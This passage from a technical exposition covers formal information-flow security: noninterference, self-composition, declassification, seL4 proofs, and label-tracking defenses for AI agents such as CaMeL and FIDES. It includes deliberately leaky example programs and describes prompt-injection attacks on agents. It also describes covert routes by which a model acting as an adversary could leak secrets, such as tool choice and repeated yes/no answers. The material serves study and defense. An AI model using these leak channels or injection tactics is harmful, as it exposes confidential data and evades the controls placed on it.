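Checking the secrecy rule requires comparing only two runs at a time. If a program breaks the rule, two of its runs have the same public inputs but different public outputs, and the difference appears after finitely many steps. Clarkson and Schneider define a k-safety hyperproperty as one in which every violation appears in at most k finite beginnings of runs, and no additional runs or later steps can repair it. Ordinary safety properties are the case k = 1, and this form of secrecy is the case k = 2.

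A method known as self-composition turns such a comparison into a question about a single run. Barthe, D'Argenio and Rezk (2011), in *Secure information flow by self-composition*, developed it for secrecy. To see how it works, take a payroll service that charges a fee for processing n records. The number n is public, the director's salary is secret, and "out" is the bill, which the outside world sees:

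```
if salary > 100_000:
    fee = 2 * n
else:
    fee = n + n
out = fee
```

The method has four steps:

1. Write the program out twice, one copy after the other.
2. Rename the variables so that the copies share none. The first copy uses n1, salary1, fee1 and out1, and the second uses n2, salary2, fee2 and out2.
3. Assume at the start that the public inputs are equal. Assume nothing about the secret ones.
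4. Assert at the end that the public outputs are equal.

The result is an ordinary program:

```
assume n1 == n2

if salary1 > 100_000:
    fee1 = 2 * n1
else:
    fee1 = n1 + n1
out1 = fee1

if salary2 > 100_000:
    fee2 = 2 * n2
else:
    fee2 = n2 + n2
out2 = fee2

assert out1 == out2
```

One run of this program contains two runs of the original, with any two salaries. The assertion is true in every run of the combined program exactly when the original's bill does not depend on the salary. In Hoare's notation, the task is to prove {n1 = n2} C₁; C₂ {out1 = out2}, where C₁ and C₂ are the two copies. Whichever branch each copy takes, out1 ends up as twice n1 and out2 as twice n2. Since n1 = n2, the bills are equal. A less precise checker might reject the program just because it branches on a secret.

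Now suppose a hostile programmer changes the "else" branch to n + n + 1. With 20 records and salaries of 150,000 and 50,000, the combined program computes bills of 40 and 41, and the assertion fails. Anyone who sees the bill can tell whether the director earns more than 100,000. A bill of 41 is not wrong in itself, since another service might charge everyone 2n + 1.

The proof covers only the property in the assertion. The two branches may take different amounts of time, which could leak the salary through a side channel even though the bills are equal. The triple also expresses only partial correctness, so it would still hold if the program looped forever whenever the salary was high, because the combined program would never reach the assertion in the cases that matter. A separate proof that the program always stops would rule this out.

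Loops also make the proof harder. When the copies run one after the other, the verifier has to work out almost everything the first copy computed before it can compare the second. Running the copies in step is often easier, because a loop invariant can then directly express that the public variables agree after each pass. Clarkson and Schneider use this parallel form in their general theorem that every k-safety hyperproperty of a program is equivalent to an ordinary safety property of k copies running side by side. Tools and proof methods for safety properties therefore work for secrecy too, although the program to be checked is larger.

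Some properties require larger values of k. For example, a system might split an encryption key into k shares, all of which are needed to reconstruct it, and output one share per run. The rule that it must never reveal all k shares across its runs is k-safety, because it may take k runs to show a violation. Other hyperproperties are not k-safety for any k. One example is a limit on mean response time across runs, because enough fast runs could offset any finite set of slow ones.

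### How filling in details can break secrecy

Specifications often leave choices open on purpose. For example, a specification might require a payroll program to return any one employee number from the list, for a spot check of the records. A program refines a specification if it can do only what the specification permits, which means that the program's traces are a subset of the specification's traces.

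Refinement preserves every property of single traces. A program that refines a specification has a subset of the specification's traces, so if all the specification's traces have the property, all the program's traces do too. Engineers can therefore prove such a property once, for a short and loose specification, and know that it holds for every program that refines it.

Secrecy doesn't carry over in the same way. A program that always returns the number of the highest-paid employee refines the spot-check specification, even though that specification permits the same results whatever people earn and so seems to reveal nothing about salaries. Each run is permitted, but together the runs reveal who earns the most. *The Shadow Knows* (Morgan, 2007) describes the simplest form of this problem, which is called the refinement paradox. If v is visible and h is hidden, an instruction to set v to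 any value of the right type permits a program that sets v to h.

A hostile programmer could therefore leak information through any choice that a specification leaves open about what outsiders can see, as with the half-cent rounding allowance.

One remedy is to change what counts as refinement. Morgan keeps track of the set of values that the hidden variable could still have, as far as an observer can tell, and allows a refinement only if it never makes this set smaller. Suppose that h is 0, 1, 2 or 3. After v is set to an arbitrary value, all four remain possible, but after v is set to h only one does, so replacing the first assignment with the second is not a valid refinement. Morgan shows that the usual rules for rearranging programs remain valid only if we assume a stronger attacker, who sees every intermediate value of v and which branches the program takes. A program that sets v to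 h and then immediately overwrites v with 0 therefore counts as leaky. *Security Engineering in IIIf, Part II* (Kammüller, 2024) uses Morgan's solution in a security framework built on the Isabelle proof assistant.

The other remedy is a stricter kind of secrecy, which requires two runs with the same public inputs to always have the same public outputs, as in the assertion at the end of a self-composed program. Refinement preserves this property, as Clarkson and Schneider prove for all safety hyperproperties, including all k-safety ones. The spot-check specification fails this requirement because it permits two different results for the same list. Its author would have to make the choice by a public rule, such as taking the lowest employee number that nobody has checked yet.

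The developers of seL4, the verified operating-system kernel, used this second approach. They wanted to prove secrecy for the kernel's abstract specification and carry the result over to the C code, which they estimated took about a tenth of the effort of working on the code directly. In *Noninterference for Operating System Kernels* (2012), Murray, Matichuk and colleagues therefore chose a definition that rules out every open choice whose result is visible to some part of the system. They proved secrecy for 98% of the functions in the specification in under 15 person-months. They had to make the remaining functions more concrete before they could reason about them, because these functions left open the decisions through which secrets might leak.

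One place this mattered was the kernel's scheduler, which decides what runs next. *Verified information flow security*, a project page from Trustworthy Systems, the research group behind the proofs, records that the original scheduler leaked information through its decisions. The kernel had been proved functionally correct in 2009. The secrecy proof, completed in March 2013, applies to a version with a new scheduler that gives each part of the system fixed turns.

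### What Rice's theorem does and does not rule out

Rice's theorem, which Henry Rice published in 1953, is a common reason for doubting that untrusted code can be verified. It applies to properties of what a program computes, rather than properties of its text. If some programs have such a property and others lack it, no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it has the property.

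The same limit applies to the host rule. If we add a line that sends a message to an unlisted host at the end of any program that sends nothing, the new program breaks the rule exactly when the original program stops. An algorithm that could decide the host rule for every program could therefore decide whether any program stops, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can do that. The same argument works for the secrecy rule if the added line sends the director's salary.

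By contrast, an algorithm can easily decide whether a program's text contains the word "send". Restrictions on the text are useful when they guarantee something about the program's behavior, and safe programming languages depend on such restrictions.

The theorem is about algorithms that must handle all programs, so we can still prove things about a particular one. The proof for the five-line billing program took a few sentences. Murray, Matichuk and colleagues proved a form of secrecy for seL4 that covers 8,830 lines of C but not timing (*seL4*, 2013). The theorem also allows a checker that never approves a bad program, as long as it may reject some good ones.

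In every sound proof system, some programs that obey the host rule have no proof that they do. Suppose instead that every such program had a proof. Then an algorithm could search through all possible proofs while running the program on more and more inputs for longer and longer. Eventually it would find either a proof or a forbidden send, and so decide whether any given program obeys the rule, which is impossible.

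This can be a serious limitation for existing code, because people may want to run a program that nobody can prove harmless. But a code generator can usually write a program in many ways. If one version of a payroll function has a loop that is hard to reason about, the generator can write another that goes through the list once. This makes it more practical to require a proof with every program, as in proof-carrying code.

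Schneider notes that there is a method for working out what must be proved for any rule that a simple halting monitor could check. Self-composition makes it possible to prove secrecy in the same way. The generator then has to find the proofs, and AI systems have become much better at finding them, as Claude's work on the 239 fuzz harnesses showed.

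## Noninterference as a specification of secrecy

Noninterference is the standard formal definition of secrecy. It requires that changing the secret inputs never changes the public outputs that an observer sees. Its many versions differ mainly in who the observer is and what counts as an output.

### From deleted commands to equal inputs

Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, defined noninterference for a machine that several people share. Users issue commands, the commands change the machine's state, and each user sees some output. Take any sequence w of commands, and let purge(w, G) be the same sequence without the commands of a group of users G. The group G does not interfere with user u if, for every w,

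output to u after w = output to u after purge(w, G)

Suppose HR staff enter salaries on a company computer and visitors look at its public staff page. Noninterference requires that visitors see exactly the page they would have seen if HR had never used the computer.

A program that runs once from start to finish has no users typing commands, so the modern version compares inputs instead. Call two memories m₁ and m₂ low-equivalent, written m₁ =L m₂, if they agree on every public variable. A program c satisfies noninterference if the following holds for all m₁ and m₂:

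if m₁ =L m₂, and c takes m₁ to m₁′ and m₂ to m₂′, then m₁′ =L m₂′

The final assertion of a self-composed program checks exactly this. The modern version is slightly weaker than the original 1982 definition, because it requires a program to hide the values of secrets but not the fact that something secret happened. A program that processes the salaries and then prints "done" satisfies the modern version but violates the original, because visitors who see "done" learn that HR has been at work.

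Both versions forbid any influence, even if it is disguised. A hostile programmer can't get around them by scrambling a salary before sending it, because the scrambled number still depends on the salary.

### Labels for secrecy and integrity

Real systems have more than two kinds of data, so each variable gets a security label. The labels have an order, and information may flow from x to y only if label(x) ≤ label(y). In the simplest case the labels are L (low, or public) and H (high, or secret), with L ≤ H, so public data may flow into secret variables but not the reverse. Any two labels a and b also have a least upper bound, written a ⊔ b, which is the label for data derived from both. An ordered set of this kind is called a lattice.

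In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025), a document's label can also be the set of people who may read it. If A, B and C may read one document, and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a summary of both.

The same mathematics can specify integrity, the protection of data from corruption. Here the labels are T (trusted) and U (untrusted), with T ≤ U, so untrusted data may not flow into trusted variables. For example, if employees can add free-text comments to their records, noninterference requires that no comment can change the amount of a salary payment. This rules out some unintended effects and is also relevant to prompt injection, in which a stranger's text steers an AI agent.

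### A type system for information flow

In the 1970s, Dorothy Denning worked out how a compiler could check labels, but she argued only informally that the checks were sufficient. In *A Sound Type System for Secure Flow Analysis* (1996), Volpano, Smith and Irvine recast the checks as a type system and proved that every program it accepts satisfies noninterference. A type system is a set of rules for accepting or rejecting a program based on its text. Most type systems prevent errors such as adding a number to a word, but the types in this one are security labels.

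The rules are easiest to follow with a program-counter label, pc, as in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit* (Askarov, Hunt and colleagues, 2008). This label starts at L and records the secrecy of what someone could infer from the program reaching a given line.

- The label of an expression is the least upper bound of the labels of its variables. Constants are L.
- The checker accepts an assignment x = e only if label(e) ⊔ pc ≤ label(x).
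- For two commands in a row, it checks each with the same pc.
- For "if e", it checks both branches with pc raised to pc ⊔ label(e). After the branches, pc returns to its old value.
- For "while e", it checks the body of the loop with pc raised in the same way.

Let "salary" be H and "out" be L. The assignment `out = salary` is an explicit flow, because it copies the secret directly. The assignment rule requires H ≤ L, which is false, so the checker rejects it. An implicit flow leaks through the choice of which line to run:

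```
out = 0
if salary > 100_000:
    out = 1
```

Both assignments use constants, but `out` still reveals whether the director earns more than 100,000. The checker rejects the program because it raises pc to H inside the branch, and `out = 1` would then require H ≤ L, which is false.

This example also shows why it helps to check the program's text instead of monitoring a run. A monitor could label each value according to the data and branches that produced it. If the salary is low, the program skips the branch, and the monitor detects only a constant being assigned to a public variable. But the 0 that remains in "out" reveals as much about the salary as a 1 would. The type checker catches the leak because it examines the branch that didn't run.

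The proof that the rules work compares two runs of an accepted program that start from low-equivalent memories. Any expression assigned to a public variable contains only public variables, so both runs compute the same value. If a branch condition is public, both runs take the same branch. If it depends on a secret, they may take different branches, but pc is H in both, so neither branch can change a public variable and the two memories still agree on public variables afterward. The same argument covers loops, provided both runs exit them.

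Proofs of this kind are now fairly easy to check by machine. *Verifying Type Soundness for Nontransitive Information Flow Security* (2026) presents proofs for this type system and a variant in 635 lines of Dafny, a language with a built-in verifier. An earlier machine-checked proof used Isabelle.

### What the types reject, and what they depend on

Such simple rules reject some harmless programs. One is the earlier billing program, which sets `fee` to `2 * n` or to `n + n`, depending on the director's salary, and then copies it to `out`. Because `fee` gets its value inside a branch on a secret, it has to be H, and the checker rejects `out = fee`. The rules ignore arithmetic, so the checker can't establish that both branches give the same value. Self-composition can establish this, but it needs a prover that can reason about what the program computes, whereas type checking is quick and automatic.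 A code generator can avoid the problem here by writing `out = 2 * n`, which the checker accepts.

The rules must also cover every feature of the language. In an example from *Principles of Secure Information Flow Analysis*, a program takes an array of zeros, sets the entry at position "secret" to 1, then searches the array for the 1 and publishes its position. The position is secret even though the value 1 isn't, so a sound rule for arrays has to treat the position as information that flows into the array. Volpano and colleagues found that their theorem no longer holds when the language includes certain other features, such as an operator that lets the programmer declare an untrusted value trusted. With that operator, it is hard to state what the type system still guarantees.

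The labels on inputs and outputs are part of the specification, so the person who wants the secret kept must set them. If the code generator could label salaries as public, code that leaks them would pass the check. The labels on internal variables matter less because the checker can infer them from the input and output labels.

### What the observer can see

The modern formula compares final memories, and only when both runs stop. In lecture slides, Chong, a computer scientist at Harvard, points out that this implicitly assumes an attacker who ignores runs that never stop. Researchers have defined stronger versions for attackers who can see more:

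| Version of noninterference | What the observer sees | A leak that it rules out |
|---|---|---|
| Termination-insensitive | Public results of runs that stop | Copying a salary to a public variable |
| Termination-sensitive | Also whether the program stops | Looping forever if the salary is high |
| Timing-sensitive | Also how long the program takes | Pausing for longer when the salary is higher |
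| Probabilistic | How often each public result occurs | Usually returning a secret bit, and otherwise a random one |

For programs that make random choices, probabilistic noninterference requires each public result to have the same probability for every value of the secret. Volpano and colleagues note that their theorem fails even for `z = rand()`, with z public, because two runs from the same memory can end differently. Requiring only that the set of possible results be the same for every secret would allow this program, but it would also allow leaks. For example, a program that returns a secret bit 99% of the time and a random bit otherwise would pass, because both results are possible whatever the secret is, yet its output equals the secret 99.5% of the time.

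Programs with several threads, which run at the same time and share variables, can turn a difference in timing into a difference in output. Suppose one thread does a long calculation only if the director earns more than 100,000, and in either case then sets "out" to 1. Another thread waits briefly and sets "out" to 0. The type rules accept each thread by itself, because neither changes a public variable inside a branch on the secret. But if the salary is high, the first thread finishes last and "out" ends as 1, whereas if it is low, "out" ends as 0. An observer can therefore learn about the salary from the output without measuring time, so a definition for concurrent programs has to account for how the system schedules the threads.

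### How much leaks when termination is ignored

The type rules enforce only the termination-insensitive version. Researchers often defended this by arguing that whether a program stops is a single yes-or-no fact, so a run can leak at most one bit. Askarov and colleagues showed that the argument fails for programs that produce output as they go. Their example, adapted to the payroll, is:

```
for i in range(max_salary + 1):
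    output(i)
    if i == salary:
        while True:
            pass
```

The program counts upwards, printing each number, and loops forever when it reaches the director's salary, so the last number it prints is the salary. The type rules accept it because the outer loop depends only on public data, which makes it acceptable to print the counter i, and because the branch on the secret changes no public variable. Three information-flow checkers accepted such programs: Jif for Java, FlowCaml for a version of ML, and the SPARK Examiner for Ada. A program that crashes at the salary instead of looping forever leaks it just as well.

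Askarov and colleagues analyze how much such programs can leak by tracking the attacker's knowledge, which they define as the set of secrets consistent with the output so far. In the termination-sensitive version of noninterference, no output may shrink this set. The termination-insensitive version lets the attacker learn from the existence of another output, but not from its value. Each new number in the counting program therefore rules out only one candidate, the salary at which the program would already have stopped.

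They proved that no accepted program can leak a secret fundamentally faster than this. Learning an N-bit secret with certainty takes on the order of 2ᴺ outputs. If the secret is uniformly random, seeing t outputs improves an attacker's chance of guessing it by at most t/2ᴺ. On a 3 GHz processor, the attack recovered a 32-bit number in under six seconds. At that rate, recovering a credit card number of about 50 bits would take about 18.5 days, and recovering a 128-bit encryption key would be infeasible.

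Termination-insensitive noninterference protects long random keys well, but not salaries. At the measured rate, a program could count through every salary up to a million in less than two milliseconds. The remedy is either to forbid loops that depend on secrets, which excludes many useful programs, or to prove separately that the program always stops without crashing. The AI-written proofs for the 239 fuzz harnesses already show termination without crashes for real C code.

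### Noninterference for an operating system

The largest well-known result of this kind is the proof for seL4, a verified operating-system kernel. The kernel divides the machine into partitions, and a policy lists which partitions may send information to which others. Murray and colleagues proved that a partition's contents after any number of steps depend only on the scheduler and the partitions that the policy allows to influence it, directly or through intermediaries. The policy need not be transitive. It can let A send to B and B send to C without letting A send to C directly, which is useful if B is a filter.

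This definition, like the modern formula and unlike the 1982 one, hides the contents of other partitions but not the fact that they ran. There would be no point in hiding that fact, because partitions take turns on a fixed schedule that everyone may know. The definition is also termination-insensitive, which is harmless here because the functional correctness proof shows that every kernel step finishes.

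The proof assumes that all the programs in the partitions are malicious, work together, and know the code and configuration of the whole system, so none of them needs its own proof. For the channels in the model, this comes close to Lampson's goal of confining an arbitrary program. An owner could put an unread, AI-generated payroll program in a partition with no outgoing channel, and the kernel would keep the salaries in. But the protection is coarse, because once the partition has an outgoing channel, the kernel doesn't distinguish a department average from an individual salary.

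Besides the trusted base described earlier, the theorem requires the owner to configure the system in particular ways:

- The only interrupt that may be on is the timer. Device drivers therefore have to keep asking their devices for news.
- Devices may not access memory directly, because the hardware model does not cover this.
- Channels between partitions must be permanent. seL4 destroys an object when the last reference to it disappears, so deleting a reference has different effects depending on whether another partition still has one. To close this channel, the initial set-up stores a spare copy of every such reference where no partition can delete it.

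The problem with deletion surprised even people who had worked on seL4 for years. It came to light during the proof attempt, because the statement being proved was false without the extra condition. The project took about 51 person-months, 23 of which went into removing nondeterminism from the kernel's specification.

Such proofs also need updating when the hardware changes. In a September talk, Barry (2026) described extending seL4's security proofs to 64-bit Arm processors. The new version had to account for registers for virtual processors and floating-point arithmetic, whose contents can survive a switch from one program to another. Sison (2026) reported in *Where are we with time protection?* that work on verifying protection against timing channels was still under way that month.

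### Tracking flows in AI agents

An AI agent that reads email and calls tools may leak secrets through those tools, and text from a stranger may change what the agent does. Two systems from 2025, CaMeL and FIDES, address both information-flow problems by tracking labels on data while the agent runs.

In Google DeepMind's CaMeL, a privileged language model turns the user's request into a short program in a restricted form of Python. This model never reads untrusted text, as Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues explain in *CaMeLoT* (2026). A second, quarantined model reads that text and extracts what the program needs, but has no access to tools. An interpreter runs the program and tags each value with its sources and permitted readers. Before each tool call, a policy written as a Python function checks the tags and allows or denies the call.

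Suppose the user wants to message Bob, whose address is in a chat channel. An attacker who posts a false address there can't add steps to the program, because the model that wrote it did not read the channel. The attacker can still change the address that the quarantined model extracts. The interpreter has recorded that the address came from an untrusted source, so a policy can block the message.

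AgentDojo is a benchmark that gives agents ordinary tasks along with planted attacks. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stops nearly all the attacks with comparable performance on the tasks. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) reports that CaMeL is much more secure than filtering the available tools or marking untrusted text in the prompt, with a fairly modest loss of usefulness.

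In Microsoft's FIDES (Costa et al.), a model chooses one tool call at a time, as usual. Nobody can tell exactly which parts of a conversation influenced a model's answer, so the answer inherits the labels of everything in the conversation. A single untrusted email would then block most later actions. FIDES avoids this by storing such data in variables that the model can pass to tools without reading. The model can also ask a quarantined model about a variable and restrict the answer to, say, yes or no. The type of the answer becomes part of its label, so a policy can allow an untrusted yes or no but still block an untrusted sentence. However, twenty yes-or-no answers can together identify any salary up to a million, so a policy against leaks would also have to limit the number of questions.

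Costa and colleagues' policies permit a consequential action only if everything that led to it is trusted, and permit sending data only to people who may read it. With suitable policies, FIDES stopped every attack in AgentDojo. It also completed on average 8% more tasks than a simpler agent using GPT-4o and 16% more using o1, though both models are now old. With the policy checks off, practical attacks got through, so the hidden variables alone were not enough for security.

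Both results fall short of noninterference. FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, which holds the sequence of actions in one run fixed and requires that it would have the same public effects if the secrets were different. This does not cover what an observer can infer from the choice of actions. Suppose an agent reads the director's salary and calls one tool if it exceeds 100,000 and another if it doesn't. Neither tool takes arguments, so no secret data enters the call, but anyone who can see which tool ran learns whether the salary exceeds 100,000. The model also excludes timing and the length of network packets.

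Costa and colleagues deliberately chose explicit secrecy, the weaker property. They argue that noninterference would essentially mean banning an agent from using any tool with public effects after any tool that might read a secret. This ban is much like Schneider's rule against sending after reading a file, and it would make many agents useless. Explicit secrecy is a reasonable choice against an outsider who plants text in an email, but it is weaker against a model that is itself trying to leak secrets.

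### Checking model-written programs in advance

CaMeL's policies apply to one tool call at a time, as the program runs. CaMeLoT adds a check of whole runs before the program starts. It converts the program into a finite set of states and labels each value by where it came from. A model checker then explores all the states to test rules, such as that no call to send money may have an untrusted recipient or amount. If some path through the program breaks a rule, the privileged model gets that path as feedback and tries to repair the program. The finite-state version allows loops to repeat any number of times, so the check can reject safe programs.

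This formally checks information flow in model-written code before any tool runs. But the rules concern the sources of a call's arguments and the order of the calls, and don't compare runs with different secrets.

AI-assisted comparisons of this kind exist for hardware. In *SLED-IFV* (2026), a solver compares two copies of a circuit, much as in self-composition, while a language model suggests simplifications and intermediate facts. The solver must prove each suggestion sound, and the model can't alter the property or add assumptions. For one test case, named after the Ibex processor, the solver alone had not finished after 12 hours, but with an accepted suggestion it completed the proof in 55.8 seconds, not counting the time spent finding the suggestion. The method also includes a deliberately leaky control to check that the set-up can detect a leak.

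The model did not write the circuits in that work, and published noninterference proofs for programs written by language models seem to be rare. The obstacle is probably not technical, since a model could write in a language with security labels and a type checker could accept or reject the result in moments. A more basic difficulty is that many useful programs do not satisfy noninterference.

### Why the payroll function fails

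For two engineers who earn 70,000 and 90,000, the payroll function returns an average of 80,000. If the second salary is 110,000 instead, it returns 90,000. The public inputs, which are the departments, are the same in both runs, but the public output differs, so returning the correct average violates noninterference.

The type rules reject "honest" for the same reason. The variable "total" is a sum of salaries, so it and any average computed from it are H, while the result is supposed to be L. Only "count" could be L, because it depends only on departments. A payroll function that satisfies noninterference can therefore report how many people work in each department, but nothing about what they earn.

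Labelling the averages H would satisfy the checker, but then only people with permission to read individual salaries could read them. The company wants the averages to be the only thing outsiders see that depends on the salaries.

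## Specifying the disclosures a program may make

Almost every useful program that handles secrets has to reveal something about them. A login page reveals that a wrong guess is not the password, and a payroll report reveals each department's average pay. Noninterference forbids both disclosures. Strict rules about information flow can also reduce the number of tasks a system completes. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports a test of CaMeL, an agent system that tracks labels on data, on 16 banking tasks run three times each. With GPT-5.2, CaMeL completed 32 of the 48 runs with its security policies off and 18 with them on.

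Specifications therefore need exceptions. Such an exception is usually called declassification, a deliberate, specified release of information that depends on secrets. It is hard to word the exception so that a program can't use it to release anything else.

### What, who, where and when

Sabelfeld and Sands, in *Declassification*, sort release policies along four dimensions: what information the program releases, who controls the release, where in the system the release happens, and when. For the payroll report, a policy might let the program release the average for each department, under the HR office's control, at one line of the reporting function, and only after the month's payroll has closed. The policy must also name the recipients, which it can do with a label that specifies the set of permitted readers.

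A policy that covers only one dimension is easy to abuse. Sabelfeld and Sands give the example of a shop that may log at most four digits of a customer's card number for each purchase. This limits what the shop releases but not who picks the digits. An attacker who can pick them can collect all 16 in four purchases.

Timing matters in a sealed-bid auction because an early leak lets a rival adjust a bid. *Generalized Security-Preserving Refinement for Concurrent Systems* (2025) includes a verified auction server that handles many bids at once. The server must keep every bid secret until the auction closes, and may then reveal only who bid the most. *Sound Enforcement of Dynamic Release Information Flow Policy* (2026) writes such conditions into the labels, and also covers rules that later become stricter again. Once the rules tighten, a program may repeat what it has already revealed only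 if the policy is "persistent" rather than "transient".

Real programs can need many exceptions. *Dimensions of Declassification in Theory and Practice* describes a poker program for players who don't trust each other, written in about 4,500 lines of Jif, a security-typed language. The program declassifies data at 14 points, and a table lists what each one releases, to whom or by whom, and at which stage of the game. A person can review 14 table entries much more easily than 4,500 lines of code.

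### Delimited release

The payroll company wants outsiders to learn the averages and nothing else about salaries. Sabelfeld and Myers, in *A Model for Delimited Information Release*, turned this kind of wish into a formula. The policy is a list of expressions e₁, …, eₙ, called escape hatches, whose values the program may reveal. Write eᵢ(m) for the value of eᵢ in memory m. With only public and secret data, a program c satisfies delimited release if the following holds for all starting memories m₁ and m₂:

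if m₁ =L m₂, and eᵢ(m₁) = eᵢ(m₂) for every i, and c takes m₁ to m₁′ and m₂ to m₂′, then m₁′ =L m₂′

This is noninterference with one extra condition, that the two memories agree on every escape hatch. With no escape hatches, it is exactly noninterference.

For the payroll function, the escape hatches are the department averages. Suppose the two engineers earn 70,000 and 90,000 in one memory, and 60,000 and 100,000 in the other. The average is 80,000 in both, so the public outputs must be identical. "honest" returns 80,000 for both memories and passes. "leaky" sends different records to the stranger's computer and fails, provided the model treats network traffic as public output. If the second engineer earned 110,000 instead of 90,000 in the first memory, the averages would differ and the formula would allow the public outputs to differ too.

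The formula also stops a program from using the half-cent rounding allowance to leak other payroll data. Two payrolls with the same averages must produce the same digits, so the spare decimal places can't reveal anything about a payroll except its averages.

Sabelfeld and Myers designed the definition to stop what they call laundering, which is using a permitted release to reveal something else. Here is their main example in payroll form:

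```
for i in range(len(salaries)):
    salaries[i] = director_salary
avg = declassify(sum(salaries) / len(salaries), L)
```

The last line has the same form as the permitted release, but by then the loop has set every entry to the director's salary. Delimited release evaluates the escape hatches in the starting memory, before the loop runs. It rejects the program because two payrolls can start with the same average but different salaries for the director, and then produce different outputs.

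The type system enforces this by forbidding programs from changing a variable and later using it in a release. The check is automatic, but it rejects some harmless programs, such as one that replaces a secret number with its parity (odd or even) and then releases the result.

In the original definition, the escape hatches are whatever expressions appear inside `declassify`. This is reasonable for careful programmers, who have to spell out what they release, but it gives no protection against an untrusted author, who can write `declassify(director_salary, L)` and satisfy the definition. Sabelfeld and Myers mention that a separate interface could list the escape hatches, but they omit it because their mathematics doesn't need it. For AI-generated code, the separate list is essential, and the code generator must not be able to edit it. *Picachv* (2025), a formally verified system for data analytics,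 takes a similar approach by having the data's owner specify the permitted operations, for example that only the average of an age column may become public.

The owner also has to understand what an escape hatch permits. Sabelfeld and Sands point out that two escape hatches are equivalent if each determines the other. Suppose the owner allows the program to publish a hash of each salary, a scrambled value that is hard to reverse. The definition does not depend on how hard it is to work backward from a released value. If no two salaries have the same hash, any two memories that agree on the hashes agree on the salaries, so the program may also publish the salaries themselves.

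Delimited release also does not require the release to happen at the `declassify` line, so a program can reveal the same value elsewhere and still pass. Askarov and Sabelfeld's *Localized Delimited Release* combines the "what" and "where" dimensions because a policy needs both to prevent laundering.

### How permitted averages reveal a salary

A program can satisfy delimited release and still reveal somebody's salary. In the simplest case, a department has only one employee and the policy lists the department's average salary as an escape hatch, so the program may publish that employee's salary.

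The owner can fix this with a conditional escape hatch that permits releasing the average only if the department has at least five members. Department sizes are public in this example, and escape hatches may combine public and secret data, so the formula needs no change.

The five-person minimum does not prevent subtraction. Suppose engineering has six members in March, with an average salary of 80,000. One of them leaves, nobody else's pay changes, and in April the remaining five average 78,000. Anyone with both reports can calculate:

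- March total: 6 × 80,000 = 480,000
- April total: 5 × 78,000 = 390,000
- Salary of the person who left: 480,000 − 390,000 = 90,000

Each report satisfies delimited release, and the department meets the five-person minimum in both months. Checking the two reports as one program wouldn't catch the leak either. Both averages would be escape hatches, and any two memories that agree on both averages also agree on the leaver's salary. The combined program would therefore satisfy the formula, since it reveals only what the policy allows. The fault is in the policy, which allows two harmless-looking disclosures that together determine a secret.

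The same thing happens with yes-or-no answers. Suppose a program may reveal only whether a customer's balance covers a given price. Delimited release stops the program from testing other prices in the same run to work out the exact balance. But a customer's rival can still find the balance by running the program repeatedly with different prices, much as a series of yes-or-no questions could identify a salary in FIDES.

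### Keeping attackers out of the decision

Robust declassification addresses the "who" dimension. Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic, in *Enforcing Robust Declassification and Qualified Robustness*, model a system as trusted code with holes in it, which an attacker may fill with code of the attacker's choice. Write c[a] for the trusted code c with the attacker's code a in the holes. Leaving aside runs that never stop, c is robust if the following holds for all memories m₁ and m₂ and all attacks a and a′:

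if c[a] looks the same to the attacker from m₁ and m₂, then c[a′] also looks the same from m₁ and m₂

In other words, changing the attack never lets the attacker tell apart two memories that looked the same before. The definition compares four runs, two for each attack. Consider a report in which untrusted code chooses the group:

```
group = untrusted_choice()
out = declassify(average(group), L)
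```

In the earlier example, one payroll has salaries of 70,000 and 90,000, and the other has 60,000 and 100,000. If the untrusted code picks both engineers, the program outputs 80,000 for either payroll. If it picks only the first engineer, the program outputs 70,000 for one payroll and 60,000 for the other. The program is therefore not robust. It would be robust if the group came from a list that the untrusted code couldn't change.

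A type checker can enforce robustness by using the integrity labels T (trusted) and U (untrusted). It accepts a release only if the released data is labeled T and untrusted data can't affect whether the program reaches the line that releases it.

Robustness suits code from an unknown author because the theorem covers any code that fits the holes in the program. The owner writes or reviews the small part that releases information, and an AI system can write the rest. The untrusted code must contain no `declassify`, leave trusted data unchanged and pass the information-flow type check. If the AI writes the whole program, including its releases, no part is trusted and robustness gives no protection.

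If AI-generated code computes the averages in the payroll function, they are untrusted data, and the type rule does not allow their release. Either the trusted part must compute the averages itself, or there must be a reason to trust the result. A proof of functional correctness can provide that reason by showing that the results equal the true averages, which trusted code would also have computed.

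Endorsement is the operation that marks untrusted data as trusted. Myers and colleagues allow it in a weaker property, qualified robustness, because many programs need it. A login page, for example, has to let an untrusted guess affect what it reveals. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026) applies a strict version of endorsement to agents. A language model may supply a file path or a time interval, but the value stays untrusted until trusted code has put it in a standard form, checked it against the policy and approved it for one particular field.

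Garby and colleagues' agent is more permissive. The model writes endorsements into its plan before it reads any outside data. On the banking tasks without attacks, turning endorsement off reduced successful runs from 36 to 30 out of 48 with one model and from 31 to 26 with another. With endorsement on, the attack succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to make a payment using the instructions in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file. Letting the model write its own exceptions is therefore a good tradeoff against outsiders who plant text, but it gives no protection if the model itself is the adversary.

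Robustness also does not limit what the trusted code releases. A trusted program that publishes every salary is robust, because no attacker can make it reveal more. Myers and colleagues present robustness as a partial answer, to be used alongside properties such as delimited release.

### Measuring leaks in bits

Some releases are acceptable only because they are small. A cash machine has to reveal whether a PIN is correct, and the security of this depends on how much it helps a thief. Quantitative information flow measures a leak as the attacker's uncertainty before seeing the output minus the uncertainty afterward. There are several ways to measure uncertainty, and Aarhus University's lecture slides *Quantitative security* (2025) compare the two main ones.

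Shannon entropy is the standard measure in information theory. If X takes each value x with probability p(x), its entropy in bits is H(X) = −Σ p(x) log₂ p(x). When a program is deterministic and the secret is its only unknown input, the leak equals the entropy of the output. For one guess at a random four-digit PIN, the output is "correct" with probability 1/10,000 and "wrong" with probability 9,999/10,000, so the leak is:

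(1/10,000) × log₂(10,000) + (9,999/10,000) × log₂(10,000/9,999) ≈ 0.00133 + 0.00014 ≈ 0.0015 bits

The other measure, min-entropy, starts from the attacker's chance of guessing the secret in one try. If that chance is V, the min-entropy is log₂(1/V). Before the check, V is 1/10,000. After it, there are two cases:

- With probability 1/10,000, the machine has accepted the PIN, and the thief knows it for certain.
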